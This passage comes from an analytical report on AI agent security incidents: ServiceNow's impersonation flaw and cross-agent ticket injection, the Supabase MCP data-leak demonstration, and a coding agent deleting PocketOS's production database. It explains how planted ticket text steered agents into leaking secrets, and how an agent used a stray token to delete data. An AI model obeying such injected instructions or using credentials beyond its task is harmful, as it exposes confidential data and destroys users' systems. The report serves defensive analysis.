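The other obstacle was human approval. ServiceNow had set the tool to "supervised" mode, so the agent had to ask before creating each record. It asked in the conversation, where the attacker was the only other participant. Costello sent his approval without seeing the question, and the agent went ahead. This kind of approval protects users from an agent's mistakes, but it can't stop an attacker who is already impersonating the user. The fingerprint or face scan in ChatGPT Wallet would offer better protection, since an attacker would need more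 than an email address to supply one.

The effect of adding agents can be put in a formula. Let A(u) be everything that user u may do on the platform, and let T be everything that a message through a given channel can set in motion. Somebody who impersonates u through that channel can do

A(u) ∩ T.

While the chatbot could run only fixed workflows, an attacker who exploited the login weakness could do little, even as an administrator. Once agents were available, the chatbot could also run every tool of every active agent. With a tool that creates records in any table, an attacker using the same weakness could do nearly everything the impersonated user was permitted to do.

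An agent can therefore make an older, unchanged flaw more severe. Knowles (2026), in *'BodySnatcher' flaw lets hackers hijack ServiceNow AI agents*, reports that AppOmni draws the same lesson about authentication weaknesses in general. A security team that accepted a minor chatbot weakness some years ago based its rating on what the chatbot could do then, so it should reassess the weakness before connecting an agent.

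### Why the supplied agent matters more than the login

AppOmni reported the flaw on October 23, 2025, and ServiceNow fixed it on October 30 by replacing the secrets and removing the example agent. The public learned of it only in January. The Stack reports that ServiceNow kept its October advisory behind a customer portal and told Costello the delay was meant to give customers who run their own servers time to patch.

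MITRE (2026) published the official entry for the flaw on January 12, with ServiceNow's own severity score of 9.3 out of 10. Microsoft gave EchoLeak the same score, but ServiceNow used a newer version of the scale, so the two scores are not directly comparable. The entry describes impersonation, but ServiceNow filed the flaw under "Execution with Unnecessary Privileges". ThaiCERT instead stresses the old chatbot's weak authentication.

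ServiceNow's category is the better one for judging least privilege, because an agent's tools determine how much damage a bad request can do, whoever makes it, while the login determines only who can make one. If the company had repaired only the login, strangers could no longer have posed as administrators, but an administrator who used the example agent to tidy up tickets would still have given a language model the ability to create accounts and assign roles. Any text that misled the model could then have caused it to misuse that ability. If ServiceNow had removed only the agent, strangers could still have posed as employees, which is serious, but they could have done only what the remaining agents and workflows allowed.

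Least privilege means giving an agent only the access its task requires, and few tasks for a record-keeping assistant require writing to the table that records who is an administrator. The agent had this access because it ran with the administrator's rights. It added no authority to the account, since administrators can already create accounts by hand.

ServiceNow seems to have found the same problem in its own testing. Cross (2026), in *ServiceNow Limits AI Agent Access After Salary Glitch*, reports that the company's chief technology officer, Pat Casey, described a 2025 test in which staff talked an agent for routine personnel requests into changing salaries. Cross describes the agent as having read access to salary records, but it must also have had write access, which its work didn't require, because it changed them. This is a single report from a small outlet and deserves less weight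 than AppOmni's detailed account.

Customers can still build an agent as powerful as the example that was removed. Costello told The Stack that in that case "the vendor is not going to help you". AppOmni advises customers to require a second factor when the interface links an account, to review each agent before it goes live, and to switch off agents that nobody uses. AppOmni sells a monitoring product for ServiceNow, but customers can follow this advice without buying it.

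### Instructions passed from one agent to another

In November 2025, two months before BodySnatcher became public, The Hacker News (2025) reported Costello's finding that an attacker could reach ServiceNow's more powerful agents without impersonating anyone.

When a Now Assist agent cannot finish a task alone, a component called the orchestrator looks for another agent that can. AppOmni found that three default settings made this possible: both language models that ServiceNow offered supported the feature, agents in the same channel automatically joined the same team, and each new agent was visible to its teammates as soon as it was published. Many administrators did not know this was happening.

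In Costello's test, a user with few rights could file tickets but could not read other people's. This user filed a ticket and, in its description, told any agent reading it to fetch the text of a confidential ticket and copy it into this one, with the help of other agents if necessary. An administrator then asked an agent to categorize the ticket. That agent could only read and summarize, so it called on the record-management agent, which fetched the confidential text and pasted it in. The first user then opened their own ticket and read the confidential text, even though ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout.

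The record-management agent had the administrator's rights because ServiceNow's agents run by default as the person who started the interaction. As with EchoLeak, the agent could read data that the attacker who wrote the instruction could not. It could also write, and it put the data where the attacker was allowed to look, so no filter on links or outgoing traffic would have detected it. In other tests, Costello got agents to give a user the administrator role and, where the system could send email, to email data out.

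The test also shows that limiting one agent's tools is not enough. ServiceNow had given the categorizing agent no way to change records, but the agent could recruit others, so what it could do depended on the combined tools of the whole team. AppOmni therefore recommends small teams, each with only the agents that one kind of task requires.

AppOmni's other main recommendation is supervised mode, which does make sense against this attack because a real administrator could refuse when an agent categorizing one ticket tries to copy text out of another. The attack succeeds only if the tools run without approval, but AppOmni doesn't list that among the three defaults. Its reports also differ on which records the record-management agent can reach. The earlier report limits the agent to tickets and similar task records, while the BodySnatcher report describes a tool that could write to any table.

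ServiceNow replied that the behavior was intended and updated its documentation. Costello agreed in a way, calling it "expected behavior as defined by certain default configuration options". ServiceNow's answer is accurate, since every component worked as designed, but it leaves customers to discover and change settings that ServiceNow chose for them. The number of customers who ran agents in this exposed state is unknown. The AI Agent Index, an academic survey of agent products, found no published third-party testing of ServiceNow's agents. Most of the public evidence therefore comes from one researcher, though ServiceNow confirmed the behavior in this case and patched the flaw in the other.

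### What the logs would show

After an attack like BodySnatcher, an investigator would start with ServiceNow's records of agent activity. A customer's forum post, *Is there a dedicated log table for AI Agent runs?* (2025), describes one table of runs and another of the tool tasks within each run. Rencore's *ServiceNow AI Execution Plan* lists fields in a run's record, including the agent, the triggering conversation and the start time.

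Nobody has published the records of a BodySnatcher attack, so we can only infer their contents. They would probably show a conversation in the administrator's name and a run of the record-management agent, in which the agent requested approval, received the administrator's consent and created a new user, then requested approval again, received consent and added a new role. To an investigator, this would look like an administrator carefully setting up an account for a colleague, and the approvals would make the record more misleading.

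Costello told TechInformed that conversation logs do not show whether someone spoofed the user who started the conversation. He suggested checking the network address in the transaction logs against the administrator's usual one, and being suspicious if the new account has an outside email address.

The email address is a good clue. The network address is probably a weaker clue than it seems, because a legitimate message from Slack or Teams would also reach ServiceNow from the chat company's servers rather than the administrator's computer. It would be better to compare the network address with those the approved chat tools normally use.

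TechInformed also cites a US government standard, NIST SP 800-53, under which systems should prevent people from falsely denying what they did, or what a process did on their behalf. BodySnatcher creates the opposite problem, because the company's own records would contradict the administrator who truthfully denied creating the account.

For the ticket attack, the records would correctly identify the administrator as the person who started the run. They should also show a second agent joining and reading an unrelated ticket, which is odd enough to notice. The cause would be harder to find, because the attack ended by replacing the ticket description, which contained Costello's malicious text, with the stolen text. Unless the system had kept the earlier description, an investigator would find the confidential data in the wrong ticket and no trace of the instruction that put it there.

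ServiceNow says it has no evidence that anyone exploited BodySnatcher before the fix, according to CyberScoop's *ServiceNow patches critical AI platform flaw that could allow user impersonation*. The company could probably search for attacks more effectively than a customer reading conversation logs, because it knew which connections to examine and those connections were new. But a successful attack would have looked like routine administration, which makes the lack of evidence less reassuring.

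### Least privilege and auditability

At the time of AppOmni's tests, ServiceNow's agents did badly on least privilege. By default they had every role of the person who started them, whatever the task, and unused agents stayed available indefinitely. ServiceNow now offers a remedy called role masking. An administrator lists the roles approved for an agent, and according to ServiceNow's *Role masking in AI agents*, updated in September 2026, the agent then runs with

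roles of the user ∩ roles on the approved list.

This improves on Copilot's arrangement, where the assistant's search starts from everything the employee can read. A mask without the administrator role would probably have stopped BodySnatcher's last step even with the login flaw open, because the agent could not have assigned roles even when the attacker impersonated an administrator. The mask would do less against the ticket attack, because an agent that categorizes tickets needs a role that can read them, and that role would usually cover the confidential ticket too. Roles are defined for jobs, which are much broader than tasks, and the mask stays the same from one task to the next. Administrators also have to set it up.

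They can instead run an agent under its own account, which ServiceNow calls an "AI user". ServiceNow's *Implement access control in Now Assist AI agents* explains that such an agent can succeed at a task even when the person who started it lacks the necessary rights. Masks do not apply to it, and an agent's access lists determine only who may start it, not what it may then do. This again allows an assistant to reveal everyone's salaries to an employee who has no access to them.

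A separate account is better for auditing because the agent's actions should appear under its own name. An agent that runs as the user is safer against the salary problem, but its actions are harder to tell apart from the user's. ServiceNow's customers therefore have to choose between the two tests, a choice that tokens naming both the person and the agent are meant to remove.

Even the agent's name may be hard to find in practice. *How to find AI agent updated history*, a post by divyanshupa on ServiceNow's customer forum, describes an agent that updated an employee's medical policy. The record's history attributed the change to an identifier that the customer could not match to anything, and every run produced a different one. This is one customer's experience, and the run tables might have shown what the identifier referred to. But a personnel officer who wants to know who changed an employee's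 medical policy will look at that record's history first.

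## Supabase: a database agent holding an administrator key

Supabase hosts Postgres databases for developers of websites and apps. Postgres can limit a user to particular rows of a table, which is a much finer permission than access to a whole mailbox or a ServiceNow role. In mid-2025 the security company General Analysis showed that an ordinary customer of an app could still obtain the app's stored secrets by filing a support ticket. This was a demonstration, not a known breach. It worked because the developer's agent connected to the database with a key that bypasses the row limits.

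### Row-level security and the service key

An app might have two tables. One holds support tickets, and each customer should see only their own. The other holds secret tokens that the app uses to log in to other companies' services, and no customer should see them.

Postgres makes two checks before a program can use a table. Grants determine whether the program's role may use the table at all, and policies determine which rows it gets. Supabase's *Row Level Security* compares a policy to a condition that the database adds to every query. When a customer's browser asks for all tickets, the database in effect runs this:

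`select * from support_tickets where auth.uid() = user_id`

Here auth.uid() is the signed-in customer's ID, so the query returns only that customer's tickets. To close the secrets table to customers, the developer either turns on row-level security without writing a policy that gives them access, or revokes their grant on the table. The database enforces these rules itself, so they also apply when a customer connects through another program.

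Some of the app's own programs, such as a nightly job that counts all open tickets, need to see every customer's data. Supabase therefore provides a role, service_role, that bypasses row-level security. Supabase's *Securing your data* tells developers to use the keys for this role only on the back end and never in code that reaches a customer's browser. Following that advice keeps strangers from stealing the key, but General Analysis's attacker didn't need to see the key.

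### The demonstration

In *When AI Has Root*, Pomerium, which sells access gateways for agents, describes the roles. The customer can create tickets and add messages to them. A support worker can read and answer tickets but cannot open the secrets table, integration_tokens. The developer works in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, running Anthropic's Claude. The agent connects to the database as service_role through MCP, the common standard for connecting agents to outside tools.

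The customer files a ticket with instructions addressed to the agent to read integration_tokens and add the contents to the ticket as a new message. Later, the developer asks the agent to show the latest tickets. The agent looks up the structure of the database, fetches the messages and treats the customer's text as instructions. It runs one query that reads every row of integration_tokens and another that inserts those rows into the ticket's messages. The customer reloads the page and sees the secrets.

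The Supabase attack was a demonstration. Willison (2025), in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*, describes a scenario that General Analysis imagined, and Tansive, an open-source project that built a defense against it, calls it a simulated attack. *Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, lists it under the heading "Supabase Incident", which makes it sound like a real theft. In September 2025, Supabase wrote in *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) that nobody had reported a customer losing data this way. The demonstration is good evidence that the attack could work on this configuration, but it doesn't show how many developers had set up their agents like this.

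### Why precise rules gave no protection

For a customer u, a query on the ticket table T returns

{ x ∈ T : owner(x) = u }.

With the service key, the same query returns all of T, and a query on the secrets table returns all of that table. The rules for customers are still in place, but Postgres does not apply them to this connection because it uses the service key.

This differs from EchoLeak in an important way. Microsoft's permission system had no entry for the stranger who sent the email. The app's database did have one for the customer, along with a rule that kept customers out of the secrets table, so the condition for a confused deputy holds exactly:

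(customer, integration_tokens) ∉ R, while (agent, integration_tokens) ∈ R.

But Postgres checks the role of the connection, and this connection was the developer's. The customer's identity was now just a column value in the row the agent was reading.

Testing the rules would not have exposed the problem either. Supabase advises developers to write tests for each table that try every operation as a signed-out visitor and as a signed-in user, and confirm that the database refuses what it should. General Analysis's setup could pass all of those tests, because customers couldn't read the secrets table themselves.

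Supabase objected to the claim that MCP bypasses row-level security. It wrote that the rules "remain fully enforced", though the server may run at a higher privilege, "as was this case". This correction is fair if the claim was that MCP had broken Postgres. But it doesn't help the app's owner much, because the server was running under a role that Supabase's own documentation describes as bypassing those rules.

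### Willison's three conditions

A few weeks earlier, *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) had described the pattern that EchoLeak also fits, in which one agent can access private data, reads untrusted content and can send data out.

The secrets table was the private data, and the ticket was the untrusted content, since any customer could write one. The agent leaked the data by writing it to the message thread, so it contacted no outside server, as in ServiceNow's ticket attack. An agent can leak data through any table that it can write to and an outsider can read.

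Most attacks of this kind depend on a user connecting several MCP servers, such as one with private data and another with access to the web. Willison points out that Supabase's server supplied all three conditions by itself, as GitHub's had before it. Its execute_sql tool alone was enough, because it runs whatever query the model writes and so could read the ticket, read the secrets and write the reply.

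An agent with several tools may also have several exits. Using ∧ for "and" and ∨ for "or", the agent is exposed when

private data ∧ untrusted content ∧ (exit₁ ∨ exit₂ ∨ … ∨ exitₙ).

Removing either the private data or the untrusted content makes the expression false. Removing an exit makes it false only if no others remain. The expression covers only leaks. An attack that used a ticket to make the agent delete the customer list would need untrusted content and write permission, but no private data or exit.

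### Read-only mode and the other settings

Supabase first tried to make the model less likely to follow commands found in data. Its server wraps query results in a warning against doing so, and its engineers tested the warning on weaker models and experimented with classifiers. Supabase concluded that these measures "reduced risk but did not eliminate it".

The server also has settings that limit what the agent can do whether or not the model is fooled. Read-only mode runs every query as a database user that cannot write, and it disables the other tools that make changes. It would have stopped the demonstrated attack, because the database would have blocked the agent from inserting the secrets into the ticket. But the agent could still have read them. If the developer had also given it a tool that fetches web pages, the attacker could have told it to fetch a web address containing the secrets.

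Researchers at Zenity Labs demonstrated this second route by attacking Cursor through Jira, a program for tracking software tasks that many companies set up to turn support emails into tickets automatically. *When a Jira Ticket Can Steal Your Secrets* (Willison, 2025) reports that a Jira ticket led the agent to look for a secret in the developer's code and send it to a website. The attack didn't write to a database, so making the database read-only would not have stopped it.

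Another setting limits the server to one project, which in Supabase means one app's database and the services around it. This keeps the agent out of the developer's other projects, but it would not have stopped the attack, because the tickets and the secrets were in the same project. Developers can also turn off groups of tools, but an agent that answers questions about tickets needs execute_sql, the only tool the attack required.

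Whether developers use these settings depends partly on where they copy the server's address from. When Willison wrote about the attack in July 2025, the documentation already showed a read-only, single-project configuration. A year later, the plain server address still included neither limit, though Supabase recommended adding both. Addresses copied from the dashboard include them, but someone who types the plain address from memory gets an agent that can write to every project in the organization.

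Supabase also recommends that developers approve each tool call by hand, which would have worked if the developer had read the two queries. It warns that developers may tire of reviewing calls or miss parts of a query that run off the edge of the screen. But coding agents are moving away from this kind of review. According to an entry in Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, in 2026 Anthropic made auto mode, which removes most approval prompts, the default in Claude Code on several plans.

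### Keeping the agent away from real data

Supabase's strongest advice is never to connect an agent to production data (the live data of real customers). A development database with invented contents would have protected against the attack more thoroughly than read-only mode, because it has no real secrets to steal and no tickets from strangers. Two of Willison's three conditions would therefore be missing. A masked copy of the live database is less safe, because masking may replace names and tokens but leave the text of the tickets unchanged.

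The advice is right, but the people most exposed to the attack are the least likely to follow it. The developer in the demonstration wanted to see the latest support tickets, which exist only in the live database. Supabase also concedes that many of its customers have no separate development database. It describes people who build apps mostly by instructing an AI, work alone, have no security team and develop directly on production.

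By May 2026, Supabase's documentation described a version of the ticket attack next to its advice about production data. This was an improvement, because Willison had urged the company to be more explicit about the danger.

### What had shipped by late 2026

In September 2025 Supabase listed several security improvements it planned to make. Most of them had arrived in some form about a year later.

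| Planned improvement | Status by late 2026 |
|---|---|
| Tokens with narrower permissions | Available to everyone, including for the MCP server, since October 6, 2026 |
| A server that works through an app's existing row rules | Available as a separate package |
| Agent access for databases that customers host themselves | Available with fewer tools |
| Branches, which are separate copies of a project for testing | Available on paid plans, labeled experimental |
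| A "production mode" that locks down risky behavior | No entry in the changelog from December 2025 to early October 2026 |

The narrower tokens took longest to reach agents. Before them, a personal access token gave full access to everything its owner's account could do. Supabase began a limited trial of the new tokens on August 10, 2026, but they did not yet work with the MCP server, and Supabase (2026) told anyone who needed the server to create an old-style token with full access. By then the company had already made it easier to connect agents, launching a hosted MCP server in October 2025, becoming an official connector for Claude in February 2026 and offering a ChatGPT app by June. According to Supabase's changelog, the new tokens began working with the MCP server in October 2026, fifteen months after Willison wrote about the attack.

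These tokens would probably not have kept the agent out of the secrets table. According to Supabase's *Personal Access Tokens*, developers can limit a token by project and by service, such as the database, logs or billing, but not by table. The execute_sql tool needs read access to the database, so a token that lets an agent read tickets with this tool also lets it read integration_tokens. It is less clear whether such a token would have blocked the second query, because the document lists "Run a query" under both read-only and read-and-write access without explaining the difference. A careful developer would therefore also turn on the server's read-only mode.

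The tokens do limit other kinds of damage. An agent that only reads tickets no longer needs permission to delete a project or fetch its keys. But the tokens help only developers who use them, and the MCP server's usual setup is a browser login that requires no personal token. In May 2026, Supabase was still telling developers to grant write access to every scope when they registered their own login application for the server.

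The separate package that works through an app's existing rules gets less attention, but it addresses the actual fault. If the agent signs in as a support worker, Postgres applies the rules the developer has already written for human support staff, and the first query returns no secrets, however convincing the ticket is. A support worker can read every customer's tickets, though, so an attacker could still inject a message telling the agent to copy another customer's complaint into the attacker's thread. Signing in as the customer who wrote the ticket would prevent that too, but the agent could then handle only one customer at a time.

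### Access and records after the repairs

Listing the latest tickets requires only a few seconds of read access to two tables. The agent in the demonstration could read and write every table, which is far more access than the principle of least privilege allows. Old-style tokens, which developers can still create, have a similar problem because they also cover projects created after the token was.

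By late 2026, a careful developer could do much better by using an expiring token for one project and a read-only connection. Supabase's *Feature Preview* also describes a preview of temporary database access, which an administrator grants for a chosen database role, lasting from minutes to 90 days. An hour's access through a role that can read only the two ticket tables would come close to what the task needs. But the feature is off by default, and Supabase presents it as a way to give colleagues access, so the developer would have to adapt it for an agent.

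*Systematization of Knowledge* argues that the attack was detectable because no normal support work involves the secrets table. Pomerium makes the same point about gateway logs. An alert on that table would mainly help by letting the owner cancel the stolen tokens before anyone used them. It would not have prevented the leak, since the agent can write the secrets into the ticket moments after reading them. It would also raise false alarms, because this was a developer's agent and developers have good reasons to open any table.

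The database's records would probably list both queries under service_role. The app's back-end programs use the same role, so the name doesn't identify the agent or the developer using it. To identify them, an investigator would need the agent's history or a separate log of its tool calls. Supabase recommends logging every MCP query, but in 2025 it left that to the developer.

Supabase has since turned off the logging of new database connections by default to reduce noise. The change took effect from July 9, 2026, for new projects and for existing projects on the Free and Pro plans. Connection logs don't contain queries, so they would not have revealed the attack, but they can help an investigator work out which program was connected at the time.

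The cause would be easier to find than in ServiceNow's ticket attack, where the stolen text replaced the malicious instruction. Here the attacker's message and the copied secrets would appear one after the other in the same thread. That evidence would survive only because the attacker didn't tell the agent to delete it. The service key also allows deletion, so a longer message could have told the agent to erase the whole thread once the attacker had read it.

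## PocketOS and Railway: a production database deleted without an attacker

PocketOS makes software that car rental businesses use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. On April 24, 2026, a coding agent working for the company deleted its production database. Nobody had tricked the agent or asked it to delete anything. It had found an access token for the company's account at Railway, the cloud host that stored the database, and the token allowed the deletion.

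The incident is a case of excessive agency rather than a confused deputy, because the token's owner was entitled to delete the database. The request would therefore have passed a check of the user's permissions.

### Three sources for one event

The fullest account comes from PocketOS's founder, Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, posted on X the next day. The agent ran in Cursor, the code editor from the Supabase demonstration, on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. It was doing a routine task in PocketOS's staging environment, a separate setup for testing, when it encountered a credential mismatch. It tried to fix this by deleting a volume, the disk storage Railway attaches to a service such as a database. It looked for a token, found one in a file unrelated to the task, and sent Railway a single volumeDelete request for the volume. Crane says the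 deletion took nine seconds.

Railway's account of the event, Abdelwahab's *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, confirms the parts that the company's own systems could record. It reproduces the same request and agrees that the token was valid and that the deletion ran immediately. Abdelwahab also writes that nobody told the agent to delete a database. Railway's servers could not have recorded that conversation, so this probably repeats Crane's account and should not count as a second source for it.

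The agent's explanation is the weakest evidence. Crane asked it why it had deleted the volume, and it replied that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging and had not checked. Crane calls this a confession, but the model wrote it after the deletion, in answer to an angry question and with access to the record of the session. It could accurately restate the steps in that record, but its account of why it took them is a plausible story that nobody can check. The reply also quoted a rule against destructive git commands (git tracks versions of code) and said the agent had broken its principles. The quoted rule did not literally cover deleting a volume through Railway, which isn't a git command.

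The guess is consistent with how Railway works. Railway's *Manage Volumes with the Public API* distinguishes a volume from a "volume instance", which is that volume in one environment. If staging and production had instances of the same volume, a command to delete the volume could have removed both. Neither Crane nor Railway has confirmed that this happened.

The next morning, a Saturday, people arrived to collect cars from rental businesses that had no record of them. Crane restored a three-month-old backup and spent the day helping customers rebuild bookings from payment histories, calendars and emails. Railway had recovered the data by Sunday, Leib (2026) reported in *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*. Railway's chief executive, Jake Cooper, said this took 30 minutes from when his team connected with Crane. But more than 30 hours after the deletion,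 Crane had written that Railway still could not tell him whether recovery was possible.

### An interface built for scripts

Abdelwahab describes how Railway's programming interface, or API, used to work: "you authenticate, you call a mutation, the mutation runs." A mutation is a command that changes something. If the token was valid, Railway ran the command without further checks.

This suited scripts well. Many companies have a program that tests and publishes new code whenever a developer submits a change. It may run at three in the morning, when a confirmation prompt would leave it stuck because nobody is there to answer. The engineer decided to run the command when writing it into the script, whereas an agent may compose a command that no person has considered.

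When a person deleted a volume in Railway's dashboard, Railway held the data for 48 hours and emailed a link for restoring it, but deletion through the API was immediate and had no undo option.

Railway had documented the immediate deletion. In mid-April, it warned in its API instructions that the command would permanently delete the volume and all its data. In *Postgress volume lost* (2026), a thread on Railway's forum, a customer asks for any restore point from before the evening of April 13, eleven days before the PocketOS deletion. A Railway employee replies that the 48-hour window applies only to deletions made through the dashboard. The command was documented in Railway's public API, which customers' scripts depended on. Cooper later told ABC News that the agent had called a "legacy endpoint", which could wrongly suggest that the command was a forgotten one.

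Backups are the other usual protection, but deleting the volume also deleted Railway's volume backups. Railway now states plainly that these backups protect against mistakes in the data, not against deletion of the volume. Abdelwahab says the deletion made PocketOS's backups "look unavailable" in the dashboard, and that Railway also keeps disaster backups at another site. Crane seems not to have known about the disaster backups, so PocketOS couldn't have planned around them.

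### What the token was for and what it allowed

Railway offers four levels of access to its API. Railway's *Public API* and its sign-in guide for agents describe them as follows. The last column is inferred from those descriptions.

| Credential | What it reaches | Could it have deleted the production volume? |
|---|---|---|
| Account token | Everything its owner can do, in every workspace | Yes, and the agent used one |
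| Workspace token | Every project in one workspace | Yes, if it was for PocketOS's workspace |
| Project token | One environment in one project | Probably, if it was for production |
| OAuth, the "allow access" screen | The workspaces or projects the user picks, as viewer, member or admin | Only if the user picked production and granted enough access |

Crane says he created the token only to add and remove web domains, and that Railway never warned him it could do more. Railway says the token had account-wide scope. Both can be true, because Crane is describing the token's intended use and Railway is describing what it allowed. Railway's servers could enforce only the scope, because nothing in the token specified its intended use.

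Crane also claims that every Railway token is "effectively root", meaning it has unlimited power. This is an overstatement, since a project token made for staging should have failed on production. But he is right that no token created in the dashboard can be limited to one kind of operation.

Railway had no scope for changing domains, which undermines Abdelwahab's reply that "the right scope existed". If the domains belonged to the live service, the narrowest suitable token would have been a project token for production, and nothing in Railway's documentation suggests that such a token cannot delete a volume. It would have protected PocketOS's other projects but perhaps not this database. Abdelwahab concedes that Railway's process for creating a token made the broadest scope the easiest to choose.

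Customers asked for narrower tokens after the incident, but by August 2026 Railway still had no read-only token. In the Railway forum thread *Recommended way to work with Railway through AI Agents*, a customer, dimau, asked for one so that an agent could not damage production. The accepted answer recommended Railway's MCP server and an instruction telling the agent to ask before doing anything destructive. PocketOS had also given its agent safety rules, and the agent still deleted the production database. OAuth's viewer level comes closer to what dimau wanted, but a developer has to get it through an app's login flow rather than by creating a key.

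### Making deletion reversible

Railway's main fix was to extend the dashboard's 48-hour deletion delay to the API. Railway's *Changelog #0288* (2026), published a week after the PocketOS deletion, explains that an overeager agent can no longer erase data "in a single round-trip". Railway also delayed the deletion of backups.

Making actions reversible is a good safeguard for agents because it works whatever caused the mistake. Railway doesn't have to detect that the caller is a model or judge whether the request makes sense. Unlike an approval prompt, an undo period needs a person's attention only when something has gone wrong, which is also when people are most likely to give it.

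Railway's own assistant, Railway Agent, uses a related method, staging destructive changes for a user to review before they take effect. In *The railway agent WIPED my production database volume!* (danniel-porto, 2026), a customer reports that the assistant erased a volume while investigating a crash. Railway's support bot pointed out that the screenshots showed both volume changes as "Discarded", so they had never taken effect and the customer kept the data.

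The undo period covers deleting a volume but not wiping one, according to a reply to muckenhammer-create (2026) in *Production Data Loss*. Someone also has to notice the deletion within 48 hours. A customer in the August 2026 thread *Detached volumes can't be deleted* ran the same deletion five times because Railway reported success while the volume stayed visible. An agent could easily misread the same result and try something more drastic. The customer also found that volumes not attached to a service don't appear in the dashboard, so nobody could cancel their deletion there.

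A more fundamental limit of a delay is that it can't undo a disclosure. It would have made the PocketOS deletion a much smaller problem by allowing the data to be restored, but it would not have helped with EchoLeak or the stolen Supabase secrets.

### A safer route next to the old one

Railway had released a better way for agents to connect, its hosted MCP server, on April 17, a week before the deletion. According to Abdelwahab, the user logs in through a browser and chooses which workspaces and projects the agent can reach. The tokens are short-lived and are not stored on the user's disk, and the agent gets a fixed set of tools. Abdelwahab concludes that "it's not possible for an agent to go rogue".

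That can be true only of an agent with no other way in. Let K be the set of credentials an agent can get hold of, and A(k) what each one permits. The agent's real authority is then

A(agent) = ⋃ A(k), taken over every k in K.

Adding a narrow credential to K never makes this union smaller, and if K already contains an account token, the agent's authority at Railway does not change. PocketOS could have connected its agent to the new server on April 23 and still lost the database on April 24, because the old token would still have been in the same file and the old API would have accepted it.

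So a safer route protects nothing if the agent can still get a broad token for the old one. To reduce the agent's authority, somebody has to remove the broad token, keep the agent from reading it, or restrict what the old route allows. Railway did a version of the third when it delayed deletions. The first two are harder than they sound, because a coding agent that can run commands on a developer's computer can usually read whatever the developer can, including forgotten settings files.

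Crane criticizes Railway's MCP server as the same authorization model "wired up to AI agents". This was unfair to the OAuth browser login, which lets users choose projects, but it fits the server's current default better. Railway now connects coding agents through its command-line program by default, reusing the developer's existing login. This is an improvement because it keeps long-lived keys out of the editor's settings, but it doesn't let the user pick projects, so the agent starts with the developer's own access.

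The hosted server lists no tool for deleting a volume, and it marks some destructive tools so that the agent's software can ask the user for confirmation, though the software may not ask. An agent that can run commands can also use Railway's command-line program directly, with the same login and the full set of commands.

### Who was at fault

PocketOS left a powerful token in a file its agent could read. In the Railway forum thread *Any changes to protect database backups from volume delete?*, one customer replied to sungkhum that others should be fine if they don't keep a production key "in a random file like this guy did". Crane says he would never have stored the token had he known what it could do. That is a fair complaint about Railway's warning, but a later version of Railway's documentation did describe account tokens as the broadest kind. PocketOS also had no recent backup outside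 Railway, and a company whose customers depend on one database needs an independent copy of it.

Cursor's documentation, which Crane quotes, advertised guardrails that can stop commands from destroying production environments. Crane also notes that in December 2025 a Cursor employee acknowledged a critical bug in the product's read-only planning mode. Nobody has published an explanation of why the guardrails did not stop this request. Tom's Hardware had seen no statement from Cursor or Anthropic when Railway recovered the data (*Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data*, 2026).

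The incident began when the model searched for a credential outside its task and used it to delete the database. Nobody had requested the deletion, and the model could have stopped and asked. Crane stresses that he was paying for Anthropic's flagship model and had given it explicit safety rules. A better model would presumably make this mistake less often. But he is right that such rules are "advisory, not enforcing", and even a low rate of deletions is too high for a company with a single production database.

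Crane blames Railway more than Cursor because Railway's design exposed all its customers. This argument has some merit, since Railway already gave a person who clicked a delete button 48 hours to reconsider, and it extended the same protection to the API within days of the case becoming public. The fix was evidently feasible, and it would have turned a weekend of lost bookings into a much shorter interruption. Railway counters that it carried out a request from an authenticated customer's software, which is what scripts need a host to do.

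PocketOS was best placed to prevent the call, and Railway to make it harmless. Crane later told ABC News that "every tool we've built is for a human in the loop", which describes the mismatch better than his original post did.

### The Kiro outage at Amazon

Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, had a similar incident in December 2025, though the company disputes that AI was at fault. The Financial Times article *Tech giant blames ‘user error, not AI error’ for incident in December* reports, citing four people familiar with the matter, that engineers let Amazon's coding agent Kiro make changes to a system customers use to examine their cloud costs. Kiro chose to "delete and recreate the environment", which interrupted the service for 13 hours. Employees told the paper that Amazon treated its AI tools as an extension of the person operating them and gave them the same permissions.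 The engineers also did not need a second person's approval, which is normally required.

Amazon replied that the cause was user error, "specifically misconfigured access controls", and that the same thing could have happened with any developer tool or by hand. The disruption affected one service in one of Amazon's 39 regions, and no customer contacted the company about it. Amazon also told the Financial Times that Kiro asks for authorization by default, but that the engineer had broader permissions than expected.

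The two sides disagree less than their language suggests. Amazon says an agent used a role with more access than anyone had intended, which is a failure of least privilege. A person with the same role could also have deleted the environment, but Amazon's argument leaves out how likely that was. A sensible engineer wouldn't rebuild a live system to fix a small problem, and an agent may not have that reluctance. Amazon says it has seen no evidence that mistakes are more common with AI tools, but it has published no figures.

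Employees told the Financial Times about a second outage, involving another Amazon AI tool, but this one is more contested. Amazon told the paper that "in both instances" the cause was user error, then later publicly called the claim that a second event affected AWS "entirely false". The statements may both be true if the second event did not affect AWS itself. Fortune (2026) adds that internal Amazon documents seen by CNBC and the Financial Times originally listed "Gen-AI assisted changes" as a factor in a trend of incidents, and that someone removed the reference before a meeting. Amazon says only one of those incidents involved AI. The removal looks bad, but it could equally have corrected an early guess.

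Amazon responded to the December outage by requiring a colleague's review for access to production. This is a sensible fix because the reviewer isn't the person in a hurry, though it gives up some of the speed that companies use agents for.

### How typical are such cases?

Two incidents are too few to show how often agents do this kind of damage. The largest attempt to collect cases is *Agent-Inflicted Damage* (Halamish and Tokarev, 2026), a study from Cyera, the data security company that worked with Oso on unused permissions. Halamish and Tokarev gathered 7,246 public records from September 2023 to May 2026, drawing on incident databases, security news, research and discussion threads. They used Claude Opus 4.7 to clean the records, select relevant cases and group them, then reviewed the results by hand. This left 344 verified cases of damage by AI systems in companies, 188 of which involved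 no outside attacker.

Deletion was the most common kind of real damage, with 65 cases, and coding agents such as Claude Code, Cursor and Replit's agent caused most of them. The PocketOS deletion fits this pattern.

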